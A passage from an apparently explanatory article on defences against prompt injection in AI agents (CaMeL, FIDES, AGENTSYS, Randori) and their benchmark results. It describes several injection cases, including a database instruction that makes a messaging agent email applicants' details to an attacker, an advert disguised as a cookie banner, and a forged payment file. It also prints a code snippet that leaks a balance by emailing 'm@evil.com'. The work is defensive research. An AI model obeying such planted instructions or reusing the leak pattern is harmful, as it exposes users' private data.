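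Foerster and colleagues tested this on OSWorld, a set of tasks in ordinary desktop programs, and report keeping up to 57 percent of a leading model's performance. That figure covers 109 tasks, apparently the ones that Claude Sonnet 4.5 had completed without the defence, and counts a task as solved if any of five attempts worked. The agent solved 31 tasks, or 28 percent, on the first attempt. A user would usually get one attempt, or would need a way to tell which of five had succeeded. Performance depended mainly on the planning model, so it may improve as models do.

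Writing one program also takes far fewer tokens than planning step by step. In these tests, CaMeL used 1.9 times as many tokens as an undefended agent. FIDES used 29.6 times as many because it resends the whole history to the planning model at every step.

*AGENTSYS* (Wen, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) keeps step-by-step planning but gives each tool call to a temporary worker agent. The worker reads the untrusted text and returns only values in a predefined format to the main agent. Part of the benefit comes from discarding the untrusted text after each call. In an ordinary agent's four-step tasks, attacks that arrived in the first step succeeded 61 percent of the time, compared with 6 percent for those that arrived in the third, because an instruction that stays in the conversation can influence every later step.

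This design cut attack success on AgentDojo to 0.78 percent, and the agent completed 64.4 percent of tasks, slightly more than the 63.5 percent completed by an undefended one. But few AgentDojo tasks need replanning, so this score is weak evidence of how the design would handle the charger example. The design also has a weaker guarantee than CaMeL, because the main agent relies on what the workers report and part of the protection comes from a model that checks their tool calls.

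### Agents that give instructions to other agents

CaMeL's guarantee applies to a single agent. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) connected three agents, each protected by CaMeL with no policies set. They asked the agents to send Julie a summary of job applicants on Slack. One agent read the applicants' details from a database, a second sent messages, and a third coordinated the other two. The researchers hid an instruction in the database to email the details to an outside address.

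The first agent and the coordinator both kept this text away from their privileged models. But the coordinator then put the summary into its request to the messaging agent, which treated the request as its user's words. The messaging agent's privileged model therefore read the planted instruction and added a line to its program that emailed the applicants' details to the attacker, even though each agent had followed its own rules.

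Peters-Gill and colleagues fixed this by giving agents separate channels for instructions and data, with an interpreter that keeps tool output out of the instruction channel. On a version of AgentDojo for teams of agents, the average attack success rate across five models was 12.9 percent with no defence, 0.2 percent with CaMeL in each agent and zero with the two channels.

The averages combine very different results from individual models. Without a defence, attacks succeeded 36.1 percent of the time against GPT-4.1, 1.5 percent against Claude Fable 5 and never against GPT-5.5. On a separate set of industrial tasks, protecting each agent with CaMeL lowered the task success rate of the two strongest models, Fable 5 and GPT-5.5, by an average of 13.4 percentage points. Adding the two channels lowered it by less than one point more. Against these familiar attacks, CaMeL would therefore add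 very little security to a current model while making it a good deal less useful. The reason to use CaMeL now is that its fixed program would stop attacks nobody has written yet, which a model's training might not stop.

### Following a document, and other gaps

Garby and colleagues designed a language for building agents and gave a computer-checked proof that it tracks labels correctly. This means that changing a secret cannot alter what someone without access to it sees, except by affecting whether the program finishes. They used the language to build an agent called Randori. Randori tests its program in an artificial environment before running it in the real one, so that error messages caused by hostile data never influence the program.

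Randori's program can also mark an untrusted value as trusted, which is called endorsement. If a quarantined model has to sort an email into one of eight fixed categories, endorsing its answer gives an attacker a choice among eight words, or log₂ 8 = 3 bits of influence. Endorsing free text gives the attacker much more influence. With three models, Randori completed 65 to 75 percent of the banking tasks, about as many as CaMeL with its policies off, and two of 1,296 attacks on Randori succeeded.

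Both attacks were against the same task, in which the user asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described. The attacker had replaced the file with a different payment request. One of the two successful attacks in CaMeL's own evaluation also involved this task. The agent did what its user asked, and tracking the file's origin could not reveal whether the bill was genuine. Without endorsement, Randori blocked the attack, but it also failed to complete some legitimate tasks that depend on a file. In another banking task, the user tells the agent to follow a file's instructions precisely. In Garby and colleagues' tests without policies, CaMeL sometimes wrote a program that could carry out any instructions in the file, which gave the attacker back the control that the fixed program had taken away.

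Christodorescu and colleagues point out that people often want an agent to follow instructions it finds. For example, an agent summarising a bug report might discover that the bug depends on another and usefully summarise both. They compare this to the way programs load new code while running, which has been hard to secure for decades.

An attacker can also use false information to trigger steps already in an agent's program. Foerster and colleagues disguised an advertisement as a cookie banner. The program had a step for dealing with cookie banners, so the agent clicked on the advertisement and opened the attacker's website. Checking the page's code stopped some versions of this attack but not others. A policy would not help much, because the effect of a click depends on what is on the screen. CaMeL also does not try to stop a document from producing a misleading summary.

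Some leaks come from the tracking itself. Garby and colleagues adapt an example from the 1970s, which works roughly like this:

```
rich  = True
other = True
if balance > threshold:
    other = False
if other:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above the threshold, `other` becomes false and the interpreter marks it secret. The program then skips the line that would change `rich`, so the interpreter never marks `rich` secret, and the email goes out. If the balance is lower, no email goes out. The attacker therefore learns whether the balance is above the threshold. An attacker cannot simply insert these lines, because the privileged model writes the program from the user's words, but a program could contain a similar pattern by accident. CaMeL can also leak information through its error messages and through whether a policy blocked an attempt.

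A more ordinary mistake is to trust the wrong data from the start. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL treated an untrusted value as trusted once a program inserted it into a longer piece of text. Narisetty and colleagues note that the deployed form of FIDES treats data as trusted if a developer forgets to label it, contrary to Saltzer and Schroeder's advice to deny access by default. All these systems normally trust the user's request, so an attacker can also try to get the user to paste hostile text into it.

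When a policy cannot settle a case, the system usually asks the user, which brings back the problem of people who approve everything. Even experts make this kind of mistake. Willison mentions Troy Hunt, a security researcher who fell for a phishing email while jet-lagged. Somebody also has to write the policies, which Willison finds hard even after two decades in application security.

### Whether any product requires such a design

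Parameterized queries made SQL injection rare at Google only after the company made them compulsory. Agents were far from having a comparable compulsory safeguard in 2025, when Christodorescu and colleagues, several of whom work at Google or Meta, reviewed the field. They found that agents had no reliable record of where an instruction came from, and that sandboxing against untrusted instructions was either missing or relied on the model's own judgement.

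A company may have since built such a design into a product without saying so. But CaMeL, FIDES and Progent are publicly available as research code or optional modules, which the maker of an email agent doesn't have to use.

Making such a design compulsory would require someone to label what each tool returns and describe its format in advance, because the privileged model writes code to handle results it will never see. Peters-Gill and colleagues had to add these descriptions to every tool before CaMeL worked reasonably well. They regard this as a modest, one-time job for a given set of tools, but a general-purpose agent may have to work with tools and websites its maker has never seen. A bank whose agent only pays bills and answers questions about an account could adopt the design much more easily, and would lose fewer tasks, because its developers can list in advance most of what the agent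 will need to do.
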